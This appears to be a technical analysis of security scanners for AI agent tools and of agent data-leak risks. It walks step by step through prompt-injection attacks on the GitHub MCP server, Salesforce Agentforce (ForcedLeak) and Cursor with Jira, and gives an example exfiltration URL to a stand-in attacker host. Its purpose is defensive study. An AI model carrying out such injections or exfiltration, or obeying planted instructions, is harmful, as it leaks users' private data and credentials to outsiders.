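| Group | Total | Agent Audit | Semgrep | Bandit |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Injection and code execution | 19 | 19 | 9 | 11 |
| MCP configuration and components | 9 | 9 | 0 | 0 |
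| Data and authentication | 14 | 12 | 1 | 0 |
| All | 42 | 40 | 10 | 11 |

Agent Audit's recall was therefore 95%, compared with 24% for Semgrep. Its precision was 87% because it raised six false alarms, while the other two raised none. All six came from its checks on MCP configuration files.

Much of Agent Audit's lead over Semgrep has nothing to do with taint. Agent Audit found 30 more vulnerabilities, and 20 of those were outside the injection group. Configuration files contain settings, so a taint tracker has no program to follow. To find passwords and keys left in files, Agent Audit uses more than 40 text patterns and a test of how random the text looks. Semgrep and Bandit were unlikely to do well on tests of MCP settings because they don't interpret those settings.

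Even the perfect score on injection is weak evidence that the taint stage helps. Bandit found 11 of those 19 vulnerabilities by matching patterns, and a scanner that flagged every `eval()` would find some of them too. Zhang and colleagues counted a finding as correct if it had the right file and line, whether or not the scanner had traced the right path to it. To measure what taint tracking adds, they would have to rerun the benchmark with that stage switched off and compare the hits and false alarms.

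Two of the published figures also need correcting. Bandit's recall is given as 29.7%, but its row lists 11 hits and 26 misses, a total of 37 vulnerabilities instead of 42. Its recall out of 42 is 26.2%. The error probably comes from an earlier version of the benchmark. *Security linting for AI agents*, an agent-audit project page with results from February 2026, gives Bandit the same 29.7% on a set of 19 samples, and the other percentages there fit a total of 37 vulnerabilities.

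The second figure, the 30 vulnerabilities that supposedly only Agent Audit found, is also too high. All of Bandit's 11 hits were in the injection group, where Agent Audit found everything, so Agent Audit found those 11 too. It must also have found Semgrep's one hit in the data group, since Zhang and colleagues report that Semgrep found nothing that the other scanners missed. That leaves at most 28 that only Agent Audit found. Neither correction changes the ranking.

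### Agent Audit on other people's software

On small test files written for the purpose, Agent Audit had a recall of 100% and a precision of 98.5%. Both figures were lower on the benchmark, and it did much worse in an outside test. *AgentLens* (Lv, Chen et al., 2026) compared three tools on Langflow, an open-source program for building agents, and counted only vulnerabilities that could be triggered while the agent was running. The paper's own tool, also called AgentLens, found 11, the earlier AgentFuzz found 3, and Agent Audit found none.

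Lv and colleagues blame static analysis in general, because a scanner that only reads code can't tell whether the model would ever call the vulnerable tool or whether a permission check would stop the call. This is a good explanation for false alarms, but it doesn't explain why Agent Audit missed flaws that the other two tools triggered. The single-function limit may be part of the reason, because a large application tends to spread a flow over many functions. Langflow is only one program, though, and the comparison comes from the developers of a competing tool.

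Zhang and colleagues also ran Agent Audit on the skill marketplace ClawHub. They report that the March 2026 scan covered 18,899 skills and produced 13,947 findings, 1,996 of them in the BLOCK tier. Agent Audit flagged 46.6% of the skills that contained scripts and 16.8% of those that didn't. Skills without scripts have no code to trace, so their flags must come from other rules.

These are raw findings, so their number is not a count of dangerous skills. *Agent Smith in Action* (2026), which introduces a scanner for MCP servers called SCAN-MCP, treats a finding as a candidate until a human analyst has reproduced its effect in a sandbox, an environment cut off from real systems. For *Unsafe by Flow* (2026), which tracks taint across functions in MCP servers, researchers reviewed the candidates by hand. Checking nearly 14,000 findings this way would take a team a long time.

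### How VIPER-MCP confirms a finding

VIPER-MCP automates the checking. It begins with a cross-function search in CodeQL. The sources are the arguments that a tool accepts from the model, and the sinks are shell commands, file operations and web requests. With these it looks for three kinds of flaw:

- command injection, where an attacker's text runs as a command
- path traversal, where an argument makes the tool open a file outside the folder it is meant to use
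- server-side request forgery, where an attacker makes the server send a request to an address of their choice, often one on a private network that the attacker can't reach directly

CodeQL reports the file and line of each suspected flaw, but a tester who wants to trigger the flaw through an agent also needs to know which tool leads to it. VIPER-MCP therefore lists every function in the program with its first and last lines and picks the smallest one that contains the source. It also runs a second query for the same flow to record the functions where the flow begins and ends. If that query finds no match, VIPER-MCP marks the alert as unconfirmed.

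Next, VIPER-MCP starts the server in an isolated environment and connects a test agent to it. A language model writes an ordinary-sounding request intended to make the agent call the suspect tool with a test value. Recording code at each sink logs what arrives there, because the agent's own account of what it did may be wrong.

If the attempt fails, a model gives it two scores from 0 to 10, one for whether the agent called the right tool and one for how far the test value got. VIPER-MCP then revises the wording of the request or the value, depending on which was the problem, and tries again.

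The repeated attempts are necessary because the test agents often cleaned up a strange-looking value before passing it on, for example by escaping its punctuation, which made it harmless. In effect, the model was an unreliable sanitiser that static analysis could not have detected. In both cases the developers describe in detail, the value reached the sink intact only after several revisions.

The developers ran VIPER-MCP on 39,884 public repositories of MCP servers. It confirmed 106 previously unknown vulnerabilities, or about one for every 376 repositories, and 67 of them had received CVE numbers by the time of publication. About half of the listed CVE entries are for command injection, including one in a server that lets agents run Semgrep, a tool for finding security flaws.

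### What "confirmed" means

VIPER-MCP counts an attempt as successful once the test value reaches the sink, even if the operation then fails, for example because a file is missing. This is strong evidence of a flaw when the sink is a shell command, since few tools should let an outsider write part of one. It is weaker evidence when the tool's job is to open any address it receives. One of the CVE entries reports request forgery in a server named url-download-mcp. Whether such a tool is flawed depends on where it runs. On a company's server it may give strangers a way into the private network, while on a home laptop it may do no more than a browser does.

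The test agent also received the requests as if its own user had typed them. An outsider would usually have to plant the same request in a web page or an email, and leading models now resist most such attempts. The vulnerabilities in the tools are real either way, but the 106 confirmations don't show that an outsider could exploit each one through any given agent.

The developers tested VIPER-MCP and two other scanners, MCPSafetyScanner and Cisco AI Defense, on 130 servers with known vulnerabilities and 130 without to measure errors. MCPSafetyScanner probes a running server without using its code as a guide. Cisco AI Defense has a language model judge the tools from their descriptions.

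| Scanner | Vulnerable servers found | Harmless servers flagged | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| VIPER-MCP | 120 of 130 | 0 of 130 | 100% | 92% |
| MCPSafetyScanner | 47 of 130 | 56 of 130 | 46% | 36% |
| Cisco AI Defense | 35 of 130 | 32 of 130 | 52% | 27% |

The test suited VIPER-MCP because it counted only the kind of flaw that taint tracking looks for. The Cisco scanner flagged harmless tools because their descriptions mentioned powerful functions, and it missed flaws that were visible only in the code. An analyst who lists an agent's capabilities from tool descriptions risks making both mistakes.

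VIPER-MCP missed ten servers because it doesn't look for the kinds of flaws they had, such as database injection and code injection. Agent Audit's sinks include `cursor.execute()` and `eval()`, so it might have caught some of these flaws.

### When a finding can't be confirmed

Requiring confirmation removes many candidates. AgentLens, a tool by Lv and colleagues, also tests its findings on a running agent. They report that across five popular coding agents, it generated 70 possible attack paths and confirmed 44 vulnerabilities, a ratio of 63%.

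An experiment with VIPER-MCP suggests that some of the findings it fails to confirm are real vulnerabilities. Its developers left the static analysis unchanged but had the system choose at random which failed request to revise next, instead of favouring the most promising one. The number of vulnerable servers it confirmed fell from 120 to 77. The other 43 were still vulnerable, and a tester who relied on the weaker version would have wrongly cleared them.

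The choice of model matters even more. In another experiment, the developers had five different models write and score the requests. With GPT-5.4-mini, the system confirmed flaws in 83 to 88 of the 130 servers, depending on which model was the test agent. With Claude Haiku 4.5, it never confirmed flaws in more than two servers, because the model refused to write attacks. But when Haiku was the test agent and GPT-5.4-mini wrote the requests, the system still triggered flaws in 83 servers.

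Some servers also depend on outside services, so VIPER-MCP can't start them in isolation. For all these reasons, 106 is better understood as a minimum than as an estimate of how many vulnerabilities the repositories contain.

Confirmation is slow too. On a sample of 500 servers, the static analysis took an average of 83 seconds per server and the trials took nearly 14 minutes. At that rate, one machine would need about 14 months to process all 39,884 repositories. Agent Audit scanned 22,009 lines of Python in 0.87 seconds, so a developer could sensibly run it after every code change and save the trials for a release.

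### Secrets that neither scanner follows

VIPER-MCP states that it doesn't cover information disclosure. For example, its rule for web requests in JavaScript checks only the first argument of the call, which is normally the address. The rule can therefore detect that an outsider chose where a request goes, but it doesn't check what the request contains.

VIPER-MCP would therefore miss the weather tool that steals credentials, because the credentials come from a file, which isn't one of its sources, and leave in a header, which isn't one of its sinks. In postmark-mcp, the email's text came from the model, so VIPER-MCP would treat it as a source. But the text left as message content, which isn't a sink, and the extra recipient was a constant.

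Agent Audit has the same limitation. Its benchmark includes tools that fetch any address a user supplies, but the sources that Zhang and colleagues list are all places where untrusted input enters, not places where a program reads a secret. In the previous section's terms, both scanners track integrity but not confidentiality. They would probably also miss the leak in `forward_ticket`, because that function takes no arguments and fetches the stranger's ticket itself.

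An analyst could extend the static half of VIPER-MCP fairly easily by adding credential files as sources and request contents as sinks. The trials would be harder to adapt. When untrusted text runs as a command, the recording code at the sink captures the harm directly, but a key recorded in a web request could be part of an ordinary login.

The flaws the scanners find can still help an attacker steal data. Path traversal can let a tool meant to read one folder of documents read private files anywhere on the machine and return them to the model. Command injection lets an attacker do almost anything the server's user account permits, including sending files to an outside address, even if the tool's description mentions only counting lines.

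## The GitHub MCP attack: a leak with no data flow in any tool's code

In May 2025, Marco Milanta and Luca Beurer-Kellner of the security company Invariant Labs got an AI agent to publish its user's salary on GitHub. They planted instructions where the agent would read them, and the model then copied private text from one tool's output into another tool's arguments. The agent used GitHub's official MCP server, and every tool on that server worked as intended.

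### The attack step by step

GitHub keeps each project in a repository, which can be public or private. Anyone with an account can open an issue on a public repository, usually to report a bug. Programmers propose changes to a project's files through pull requests, which anyone can read if the repository is public.

In Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025), the demonstration account had a public repository with a simple Pac-Man game and several private ones with personal projects. Milanta and Beurer-Kellner connected the account to Claude Desktop, running Claude 4 Opus, and opened an issue in the game's repository. Willison's *GitHub MCP Exploited* quotes the issue's opening, which praises the project and regrets that its author isn't better known. To remedy this, it tells the reader to read the README (the introductory file) in each of the author's repositories and write a new chapter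 from them.

The leak then took four steps:

1. The user asked the agent to look at the game's open issues.
2. The agent fetched the issues, which put the planted text in its context.
3. It read files from the private repositories, which put their contents in its context too.
4. It opened a pull request on the public game that contained the new chapter.

The pull request revealed the name of a private project, Jupiter Star, along with the user's salary and plan to move to South America. By default, Claude Desktop asks the user to confirm each tool call, and a user who read the last call carefully would have seen the salary. But Invariant Labs notes that many users choose "Always Allow" and stop checking. Many off-the-shelf injection detectors also missed the attack.

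Milanta and Beurer-Kellner used demonstration repositories, so their result shows that the leak is possible but doesn't show how often such an attack would succeed.

### What a taint tracker finds in the three tools

Three short functions are enough to reproduce the attack. These are simplified Python versions of what the server does, and `github` stands for a client that sends requests to GitHub on the user's behalf:

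```python
def list_issues(repo):
    return github.get(f"/repos/{repo}/issues")

def read_repo_file(repo, path):
    return github.get(f"/repos/{repo}/contents/{path}")

def open_pull_request(repo, text):
    return github.post(f"/repos/{repo}/pulls", json={"body": text})
```

All three are correct. The first returns issues that anyone may read, the second returns a file that the user is entitled to read, and the third writes to a repository where the user is entitled to write. A single-function taint tracker with outbound requests as its sinks gets these results:

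| Function | Labelled value | Where the value goes | Leak reported |
|---|---|---|---|
| `list_issues` | the issues (untrusted) | the return statement | no |
| `read_repo_file` | the private file (secret) | the return statement | no |
| `open_pull_request` | none, because `text` is an unlabelled parameter | an outbound request | no |

Cross-function analysis finds nothing more, because none of the functions calls another. Labelling every parameter untrusted and secret would cause the same false alarms as it did for `send`.

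Invariant Labs likewise concluded that the attack was "not a flaw in the GitHub MCP server code itself", and that GitHub alone couldn't fix it by patching the server. GitHub did add a partial defence that August. According to GitHub (2025), the server now scans tool calls on public repositories for secrets such as credentials. This would stop an agent from pasting a recognisable key into a pull request, but it probably wouldn't have stopped this leak, because a salary in an ordinary sentence doesn't look like a credential.

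### The model as a node in the graph

The connection between the functions is the model, which writes each call's arguments from a context that holds all the earlier outputs. Let o₁ to oₖ be the outputs so far and aₖ₊₁ the arguments of the next call. Then

aₖ₊₁ = M(request, o₁, …, oₖ)

where M is the model. An analyst can't read M the way one reads a Python function, so M resembles `pick_desk`, the library helper whose source was missing. For such a helper, Semgrep assumes by default that taint passes from any argument to the result. The same assumption about the model gives

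L(aₖ₊₁) = L(request) ⊔ L(o₁) ⊔ … ⊔ L(oₖ)

In the GitHub attack, the user's request is trusted and public, or (0, 0). The issues are untrusted and public, or (1, 0), so after the first call everything the model writes is also (1, 0). The private files are (0, 1), and reading them raises the label to (1, 1). So when the model calls `open_pull_request`, an outsider could have chosen the destination, and the text could contain a secret. The narrow rule for `forward_ticket` flagged the same two conditions.

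The path looks like this as a graph:

```
list_issues     -- untrusted -------------> model
read_repo_file  -- secret ----------------> model
model           -- untrusted and secret --> open_pull_request
```

The full graph has arrows in both directions between the model and every tool, so any tool can influence any other in two steps. The agent can make the calls in any order.

If the analysis must not miss any path, the analyst has to assume that any tool output can influence any later tool call. This overstates the model's behavior, since most tool-call arguments depend on only a small part of the context. But an analyst who assumed that the model passed nothing on would miss the attack. To use an assumption between these two, the analyst would have to predict which sentences the model will copy or obey, and that can change from one run to the next.

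### Three sets of tools

Let U be the set of tools that return content an outsider could have written, S the set that return private data, and X the set that can send data to a place an outsider can read. If the request is clean and nothing enters or leaves except through tools, the graph contains an attack path exactly when each set has at least one tool.

If U, S and X each contain at least one tool, the agent can call a tool from U and one from S, which raises the context to (1, 1), and then pass the secret to a tool from X. If U is empty, no outsider's text reaches the model, so no outsider can steer it. If S is empty, there is no secret to steal, and if X is empty, the agent has no way to send one out.

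One tool can belong to two sets. In the payroll example, `fetch_page` is in U because strangers write web pages, and in X because the agent can put data in the address it requests, as in `evil.example/?salary=50000`. An agent with only `fetch_page` and `read_file` therefore has an attack path, even without `post_to_web`.

The test also takes little work. In a post introducing toxic flow analysis, which builds such graphs for real agents, Invariant Labs (2025) points out that an agent may use any combination of its tools, so a reviewer has to consider every subset. Thirty tools have more than a billion subsets, but under the worst-case assumption adding a tool never removes a path, so checking the full set covers all the smaller ones. The analyst only has to ask three questions about each tool.

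Capability-combination analysis is thus taint analysis with a worst-case assumption about the model. Because it keeps the integrity label, it is less crude than flagging every agent that can read private files and post to the web. It also requires U to be non-empty, which clears an agent that reads only files its own company wrote. Only measurements on real skills can show how often the remaining flags are right.

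### The lethal trifecta, one leg at a time

Willison coined the term "lethal trifecta" for the three conditions in June 2025, three weeks after the GitHub demonstration. He bases his argument on fourteen earlier reports of the same kind of exploit, from ChatGPT in April 2023 to OpenAI's Operator agent in February 2025. He singles out GitHub's server because it supplied all three conditions by itself.

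If the three conditions are all necessary, removing any one of them from the GitHub agent should stop the theft. For example, the user could remove the agent's access to private data by giving it an access token that covers only the game's repository. The planted issue might still make the agent write nonsense or propose harmful code in a pull request, but the agent could no longer open the private projects.

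Invariant Labs suggests a milder version, a runtime rule that allows the agent only one repository per session. After reading the game's issues, the agent couldn't open Jupiter Star. The rule would also prevent some legitimate work, such as copying a bug fix from one project to another. Because it compares only calls to GitHub tools, it doesn't protect private data from other sources. For example, an agent that can read files on the user's laptop could still put one in a pull request on the game.

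Removing the untrusted content is harder. The agent could ignore issues from anyone outside the project, but the project's owner often wants help with strangers' bug reports. According to GitHub, attackers can also plant instructions in README files and pull request comments. Even without an attacker, the model might publish something private by mistake. The trifecta doesn't cover such accidents, which require only private data and a way to send it out.

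The last option is to make the agent's access read-only. The agent might still follow the instructions in the issue and read the private files, but it would have no tool for publishing them. Willison observes that vendors usually fix these exploits by blocking the routes by which data can leave. This works only if they find every route, including any that aren't in the list of tools.

### ForcedLeak: a way out that is not a tool

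Salesforce sells software for tracking customers, and Agentforce is its line of AI agents. A company can put a Salesforce form called Web-to-Lead on its website to collect details from potential customers, known as leads. In September 2025, the security firm Noma Security disclosed ForcedLeak, an attack that could steal customer data through this form.

The attacker typed instructions into the form and waited for an employee to ask the agent about the new lead. In the text, which Willison (2025) reproduces, the attacker asks how many leads there are, what colour red and yellow make, and what email addresses the leads have. The attacker then tells the agent to end its answer with a "preview image" whose web address contains the email addresses. When the page displayed the answer, it requested the image, which sent the customers' email addresses to the server that Noma's researchers controlled.

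The agent had to query the customer database, but no tool sent the data out. An analyst who listed only the tools would have found untrusted content and private data but no way to send data out, and might have cleared the agent. The analyst also has to include everything that happens to the agent's answer, such as whether images in it are loaded.

Salesforce had tried to close this channel with a Content Security Policy, a list of the sites from which a page may load content such as images. But the list still included my-salesforce-cms.com, whose registration had expired. According to Hackread's *ForcedLeak Flaw in Salesforce Agentforce AI Agent Exposed CRM Data*, the domain was on sale for $5. Noma, quoted by Salesforce Ben, a news site for Salesforce users, said that exfiltration "would have been impossible" without this gap. The case therefore tests the third leg quite directly, because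 the same injection and customer data produced no leak until the researchers had a site that the policy allowed.

The policy was a sanitiser, like the allow-list for `host` in `forward_ticket`. It stopped working because a domain expired, not because Salesforce's code changed, so a scan of the code alone couldn't have caught this. The Hacker News reports that Salesforce recovered the domain and now prevents its agents from sending output to untrusted addresses. The DNS leaks that Poireault reported came a year later.

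### Models that resist injection

The main objection to this is that the worst-case model no longer resembles real ones. Claude 4 Opus, which followed the instructions in the planted issue, is several generations old, and a current model might well ignore them.

Developers' own figures support the objection. OpenAI distinguishes direct injection, which arrives in the chat, from indirect injection, which is hidden in content the agent reads. *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (TechRepublic, 2026) says OpenAI reported in August 2026 that 3.77% of indirect attacks succeeded against GPT-5.6 Sol. *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense* (Cross, 2026) gives an October figure for GPT-6 Sol equivalent to a 2.87% success rate for indirect attacks. Direct attacks on GPT-6 Sol succeeded only about once in 10,000 attempts, but the GitHub issue was an indirect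 attack.

Outside tests can give much higher rates. *FrontierBreach*, a benchmark from the security company PromptArmor, hides attacks in long office tasks, such as analysing a bond portfolio. The table compares some of its results with other published figures for the same models.

| Model | Success rate in FrontierBreach | Success rate in another test |
|---|---|---|
| Gemini 4 Carbon | 2.4% | – |
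| GPT-6 Astra | 7.6% | – |
| Claude Fable 5.2 | 10.0% | – |
| Claude Opus 5 | 10.0% | 2.0% after 15 attempts (Gray Swan) |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 33.3% | 3.77% (OpenAI) |
| Grok 4.5 | 91.4% | – |

PromptArmor advertises the benchmark's high success rates against leading models, so it had a reason to choose attacks that work, but a real attacker also has reason to choose them. The figures for GPT-5.6 Sol differ by a factor of almost nine, so it is hard to give a single success rate for a model.

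The attack success rate depends heavily on the attacker. OpenAI gave human testers and GPT-Red, its automated attacker, the same set of scenarios against the older GPT-5.1. The humans succeeded in 13% of the scenarios and GPT-Red in 84%. Filters around the model also lower the rate. In a coding test of Claude Opus 4.8 reported by VentureBeat, extra safeguards cut an adaptive attacker's success rate on single attempts by about 70%, from 7.03% to 2.09%.

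Repeated attempts help the attacker, but less than they would if each attempt were independent. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* reports on a test of especially strong attacks from late 2025, which succeeded 4.7% of the time on one attempt, 33.6% within ten attempts and 63% within a hundred. With independent attempts, the last two figures would have been about 38% and 99%. Some scenarios seem to resist almost every attack, while in others an attack succeeds after a few attempts.

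### Why 95% may not be enough

Willison anticipated part of the objection in 2025, when he discussed "guardrail" products, filters whose vendors claim to catch 95% of attacks. He wrote that in web security "95% is very much a failing grade". An attacker can still look for the 5% that such a filter misses.

Attackers can also try many targets at once. If someone plants an issue in 1,000 repositories and an agent with all three capabilities reads each issue, the attacker can expect about 29 leaks at GPT-6 Sol's rate of 2.87%, whether or not the attempts are independent. A filter that caught 95% of the attacks that would otherwise have succeeded would reduce the expected number to about 1.4. That is a large improvement for the 1,000 users as a group, but it may not reassure a hospital or a bank that has to protect its own records.

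Resistance also depends on the model, which users can change without changing their tools. An agent that switched from Gemini 4 Carbon to Grok 4.5 would go from 2.4% to 91.4% on FrontierBreach, even though it would have access to the same files and the same ways to send them out. A flag based on the agent's capabilities would remain correct after the switch.

The objection does show that a yes-or-no flag is a poor measure of urgency. Two agents with the same three capabilities can face very different risks if only one uses a resistant model. An analyst could use the flag to decide which agents need attention, and attack success rates to decide which to fix first. But a low success rate doesn't justify removing the flag, because a test covers only the attacks that somebody tried.

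### Earlier rules about dangerous combinations

Security researchers were flagging combinations of capabilities long before language models could call tools. An Android app has to declare the permissions it needs, such as access to the microphone or the internet. *On Lightweight Mobile Phone Application Certification* (Enck, Ongtang and McDaniel, 2009) introduced Kirin, a service that checks these permissions against a short list of rules when the user installs an app. One rule rejects any app that can monitor the phone's state, record audio and use the internet, because such an app could record calls and send them to someone.

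Enck and colleagues tried the rules on 311 popular apps. They found five with dangerous functions, and another five whose permissions broke the rules but seemed reasonable given what the apps were for. Capability-combination analysis has the same weakness, because a list of permissions doesn't show whether an app is spyware or a call recorder the user wants. With an Android app, an analyst can find out by reading the code that connects the microphone to the internet. The GitHub agent has no such code, so the analyst can't check the flag in the same way.

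Kirin examined one app at a time, while *COVERT* (Bagheri, Sadeghi and colleagues, 2015) dealt with leaks between apps. Android apps can send requests to one another, so an app without permission to send text messages may be able to send them through an app that has it. COVERT extracts a model of each app from its code, then formally checks whether a group of apps could misuse a permission together. Each app might pass a separate review, as each GitHub tool would.

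*Safety is Non-Compositional* (Spera, 2026) states the general result for AI agents. It represents an agent as a set of capabilities and a set of rules for which capabilities jointly produce another. An algorithm finds every capability the agent can reach by applying the rules until nothing new appears. The agent is safe if the final set, called the closure, contains no forbidden capability.

The proof that two safe sets can form an unsafe one needs only two capabilities, u₁ and u₂, a forbidden capability f, and one rule:

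u₁ and u₂ together produce f

An agent with only u₁ can't apply the rule, so its closure is {u₁} and it is safe. The same is true of an agent with only u₂. But if the two agents combine their capabilities, the rule applies and the closure is {u₁, u₂, f}. *Capability Safety as Datalog* (2026) derives the same result in Datalog, a language for logical rules, and attributes it to the "and" in a rule that requires two conditions at once. Any system with such a rule can behave this way.

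The trifecta is such a rule with three conditions. An agent that reads strangers' emails and private files but can't send anything is safe by this test, and so is an agent that can only send messages. If the two share their capabilities, they have an attack path. The rule at the sink expresses this condition by requiring both labels. The arrows in the model graph don't express it alone, since a secret can reach `open_pull_request` with or without a planted issue.

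Spera acknowledges that the example is deliberately minimal and that security researchers have studied this kind of combination for decades. The theorem doesn't determine which combinations are dangerous, so somebody still has to supply the rules. Spera found that 42.6% of 900 multi-tool task records from public benchmarks contained steps that needed several capabilities at once. Those were ordinary tasks, so the figure shows that "and" rules are common in agents' work but doesn't measure how many agents could leak data.

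This result means that a marketplace can't guarantee a user's agent is safe by approving each MCP server or skill separately. Somebody has to check the agent again whenever the user installs another one. In Spera's model, removing a capability never makes a safe agent unsafe. An agent with four tools in U, three in S and two in X, with no overlaps, has 4 × 3 × 2 = 24 dangerous combinations, but its owner can eliminate them all by removing the two tools in X.

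## Rules that flag a set of tools: toxic flow analysis and the Agents Rule of Two

Developers can check an agent for dangerous combinations of tools with a scanner or a rule of thumb. Toxic flow analysis, which Invariant Labs and Snyk released in July 2025, scans the tools an agent can reach, labels each one, and reports the sets that could leak data. Meta's Agents Rule of Two, from October 2025, is a design rule that limits what an agent may do in one session.

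### From a list of tools to a toxic flow

Snyk, which sells security software to developers, bought Invariant Labs in June 2025, about a month after the GitHub demonstration. On 29 July, Invariant Labs released a preview of toxic flow analysis in its scanner, MCP-scan. A toxic flow is a possible sequence of tool calls that are harmless individually but together would leak data or do damage.

The analysis has four steps:

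1. The scanner lists the tools. It reads the settings of the agents on the user's machine, connects to each MCP server it finds there, and retrieves the tools' names and descriptions.
2. It labels each tool according to whether an outsider could have written its output, whether it returns private data, and whether it can send data to an outsider.
3. It builds a graph of the sequences in which the agent could call the tools.
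4. It searches the graph for sequences that would leak data, and scores them.

The score helps the user decide what to fix first. Snyk's *Understanding Toxic Flows in MCP and the Hidden Risk of AI-Native Systems* suggests basing it on factors such as how sensitive the data is, how easy the attack would be and what kind of sink the flow ends in. A flow that could send production passwords to any address on the internet matters more than one that could send harmless metadata to an internal system.

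Toxic flow analysis can also use records of what agents did while running. Snyk Labs' *Unmasking the Toxic Flow Analysis* (2025) describes this as a way to keep monitoring an agent after its first scan.

### Rule TF001

Invariant Labs' *Issue Code Reference* calls the data-leak rule TF001. It requires three components:

- an untrusted content tool, whose output could be malicious, such as one that fetches a web page
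- a private data tool, such as one that reads files on the user's machine
- a public sink tool, which can get information to the attacker, for example by writing to a public repository or sending a WhatsApp message

These correspond to the sets U, S and X in the GitHub example.

A companion rule, TF002, covers damage instead of theft. It requires only an untrusted content tool and a destructive tool (one whose effects the user can't reverse, such as a tool that deletes files or sends money).

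The scanner has since been renamed Snyk Agent Scan. According to Rubinlake's *Agent Scan*, the old mcp-scan package now installs the new one. According to a copy of the manual in TypingMind's *Snyk Agent Scan*, versions 0.6 and later replace issue codes with scored risk indicators for threats such as exposure to untrusted or private data. Snyk plans to retire the 0.5 versions, which still use the codes, and warns that the names of the new indicators may change.

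### Twelve tools and sixty triples

Suppose a company gives its office assistant twelve tools, each with one label:

| Label | Tools | Number |
|---|---|---|
| Untrusted content | `read_reviews`, `read_forum`, `read_tickets`, `read_issues` | 4 |
| Private data | `read_payroll`, `read_contracts`, `read_budget`, `read_sales`, `read_notes` | 5 |
| Public sink | `send_email`, `send_text`, `post_comment` | 3 |

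An attacker needs one tool from each row. There are 4 × 5 × 3 = 60 such triples, for example `read_forum`, `read_payroll` and `send_text`. The agent can make the two reads in either order, so the 60 triples give 120 leaking sequences of three calls.

Now suppose the company tries to fix the problem by deleting tools:

| Change | Untrusted content | Private data | Public sinks | Triples left |
|---|---|---|---|---|
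| None | 4 | 5 | 3 | 60 |
| Delete `send_text` | 4 | 5 | 2 | 40 |
| Delete `read_forum` | 3 | 5 | 3 | 45 |
| Delete `read_notes` | 4 | 4 | 3 | 48 |
| Delete all three of these tools | 3 | 4 | 2 | 24 |
| Delete every public sink | 4 | 5 | 0 | 0 |

Deleting `send_text` removes a third of the triples, but the attacker can use email instead. The number of triples is the product of the three class sizes, so the company has to remove every tool in one class to clear the flag. Deleting tools without regard to their labels usually doesn't clear it, because 3,255 (79%) of the 4,096 possible subsets of the twelve tools still contain at least one tool from each class.

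For the same reason, the number of triples is a poor measure of risk. An agent with one triple that includes the payroll may be more dangerous than an agent with 60 triples that include only old meeting notes.

A user also needs the complete list of tools in the flagged class. According to an older manual reproduced in mcp.directory's *Snyk Agent Scan*, the scanner showed only the top three tools in a toxic flow unless the user added the option `--full-toxic-flows`. Someone who deleted a listed sink might not know that unlisted sinks remained.

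### Tools with more than one label

Real tools often have several labels. Suppose the company deletes all three sinks and later adds `fetch_page`, which can open any web address and is therefore both a source of untrusted content and a sink. The assistant now has five sources of untrusted content, five sources of private data and one sink, which gives 5 × 5 × 1 = 25 combinations. In five of them, `fetch_page` both brings in the injection and sends out the data.

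A single tool can have all three labels. For example, an agent can use `run_command`, which runs any shell command, to download a stranger's page, read a private file and upload that file. TF001 would flag an agent whose only tool was `run_command`. The owner could clear the flag only by removing the tool or restricting what it can do, for instance by running it on a machine with no network connection.

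### The Jira ticket that asked for apples

Cursor is a code editor with a built-in AI agent, and Jira is a system companies use to track bugs and support requests. On 1 August 2025, Marina Simakov of the security firm Zenity Labs published an attack that used a Jira ticket to steal credentials from a programmer's machine.

Snyk Labs' *What is the “Cursor + Jira MCP 0-Click” vulnerability?* (2025) explains how the attack worked. The attacker didn't need a Jira account, because at some companies an email to the support address automatically becomes a Jira ticket. In the ticket, the attacker asked the agent to look for apples, and defined an apple as a long string that starts with "eyj", as many login tokens do. An agent told never to search for secrets might still search for apples. Once a developer asked Cursor to work on the ticket, the agent found the credentials and sent them to the attacker.

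TF001's labels fit the case neatly:

| Label | What the agent used |
|---|---|
| Untrusted content | the Jira tool, because anyone could submit a ticket |
| Private data | access to local files, which could contain credentials |
| Public sink | web requests, which could carry the credentials in the address |

Yet MCP-scan would have missed the attack, which relied on tools built into Cursor. At the time, the scanner examined only the MCP servers that the user had installed, so it couldn't find the full combination of tools. Snyk responded by adding the option `--include-built-in`, which includes Cursor's own tools in the search.

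Cursor could already read files and send web requests, so adding any server that brought in text from strangers would have completed the combination. Snyk Labs points out that public pull requests on GitHub would have worked as well as Jira tickets.

The scanner's inventory can still be incomplete. According to the coverage table in TypingMind's copy of the manual, the scanner finds servers in a Claude Desktop user's own settings but not those bundled inside Claude Desktop extensions.

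### Where the labels come from

Snyk Labs labels MCP tools using AI classifiers and a dataset of tools with known labels. The scanner sends Snyk the tools' names and descriptions, along with other details of the setup. This approach works for tools in any programming language and for servers whose code the user can't see, but it depends on the names and descriptions that the tools' authors chose to write.

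If a tool's description leaves something out, its labels will probably be wrong, as they would be for the malicious `get_weather`. A dishonest description can also hide one part of a combination. Suppose the office assistant no longer has its three sinks, and someone installs a spelling checker that secretly sends every text it checks to the checker's developer. The scanner would report no toxic flow, although the agent could again send out the payroll.

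The scanner warns the user when a tool's description differs from an earlier one (W003 in the Invariant Labs reference), because an attacker might have replaced a harmless tool with a malicious one. This check wouldn't catch an update like the one to postmark-mcp if the new line of code came with the old description.

Labels can also be too severe. If `post_comment` writes to a board that only employees can read, it isn't a public sink, but its description may not include that restriction. In *Agent Scan* (2026), the technology consultancy Thoughtworks advises teams to check the scanner's false-positive rate in their own environment before relying on it.

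Snyk warns that to collect the descriptions, the scanner has to start local MCP servers by running the commands in the user's settings. A malicious server could do harm before the user sees any results. The scanner therefore asks for permission before starting each server, and Snyk recommends an isolated machine for servers the user doesn't trust.

An analyst who has the code can derive the labels from it instead. SCAN-MCP, the scanner introduced in *Agent Smith in Action*, extracts sources and sinks from each tool's code and searches for chains of tools up to a fixed length. Some of the chains it found bypass one tool's safety check by using another tool on the same server.

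### Meta's Agents Rule of Two

Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) gives developers a rule they can apply without a scanner. It names three properties:

- **A**: the agent can process untrustworthy inputs.
- **B**: it can access sensitive systems or private data.
- **C**: it can change state or communicate externally.

An agent may have at most two of these in one session. A new session begins with a fresh context. If a task needs all three in the same session, the agent must not work autonomously and needs at least supervision, through human approval or "another reliable means of validation".

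Meta's main example is a hypothetical assistant called Email-Bot, which reads new mail, searches the inbox and sends replies. A spam email could contain instructions to collect private messages and forward them to the attacker. The developer can prevent this by removing any one property. The bot could read mail only from trusted senders, work in a test environment with no real data, or send mail only if the recipient is trusted or a person has checked the draft.

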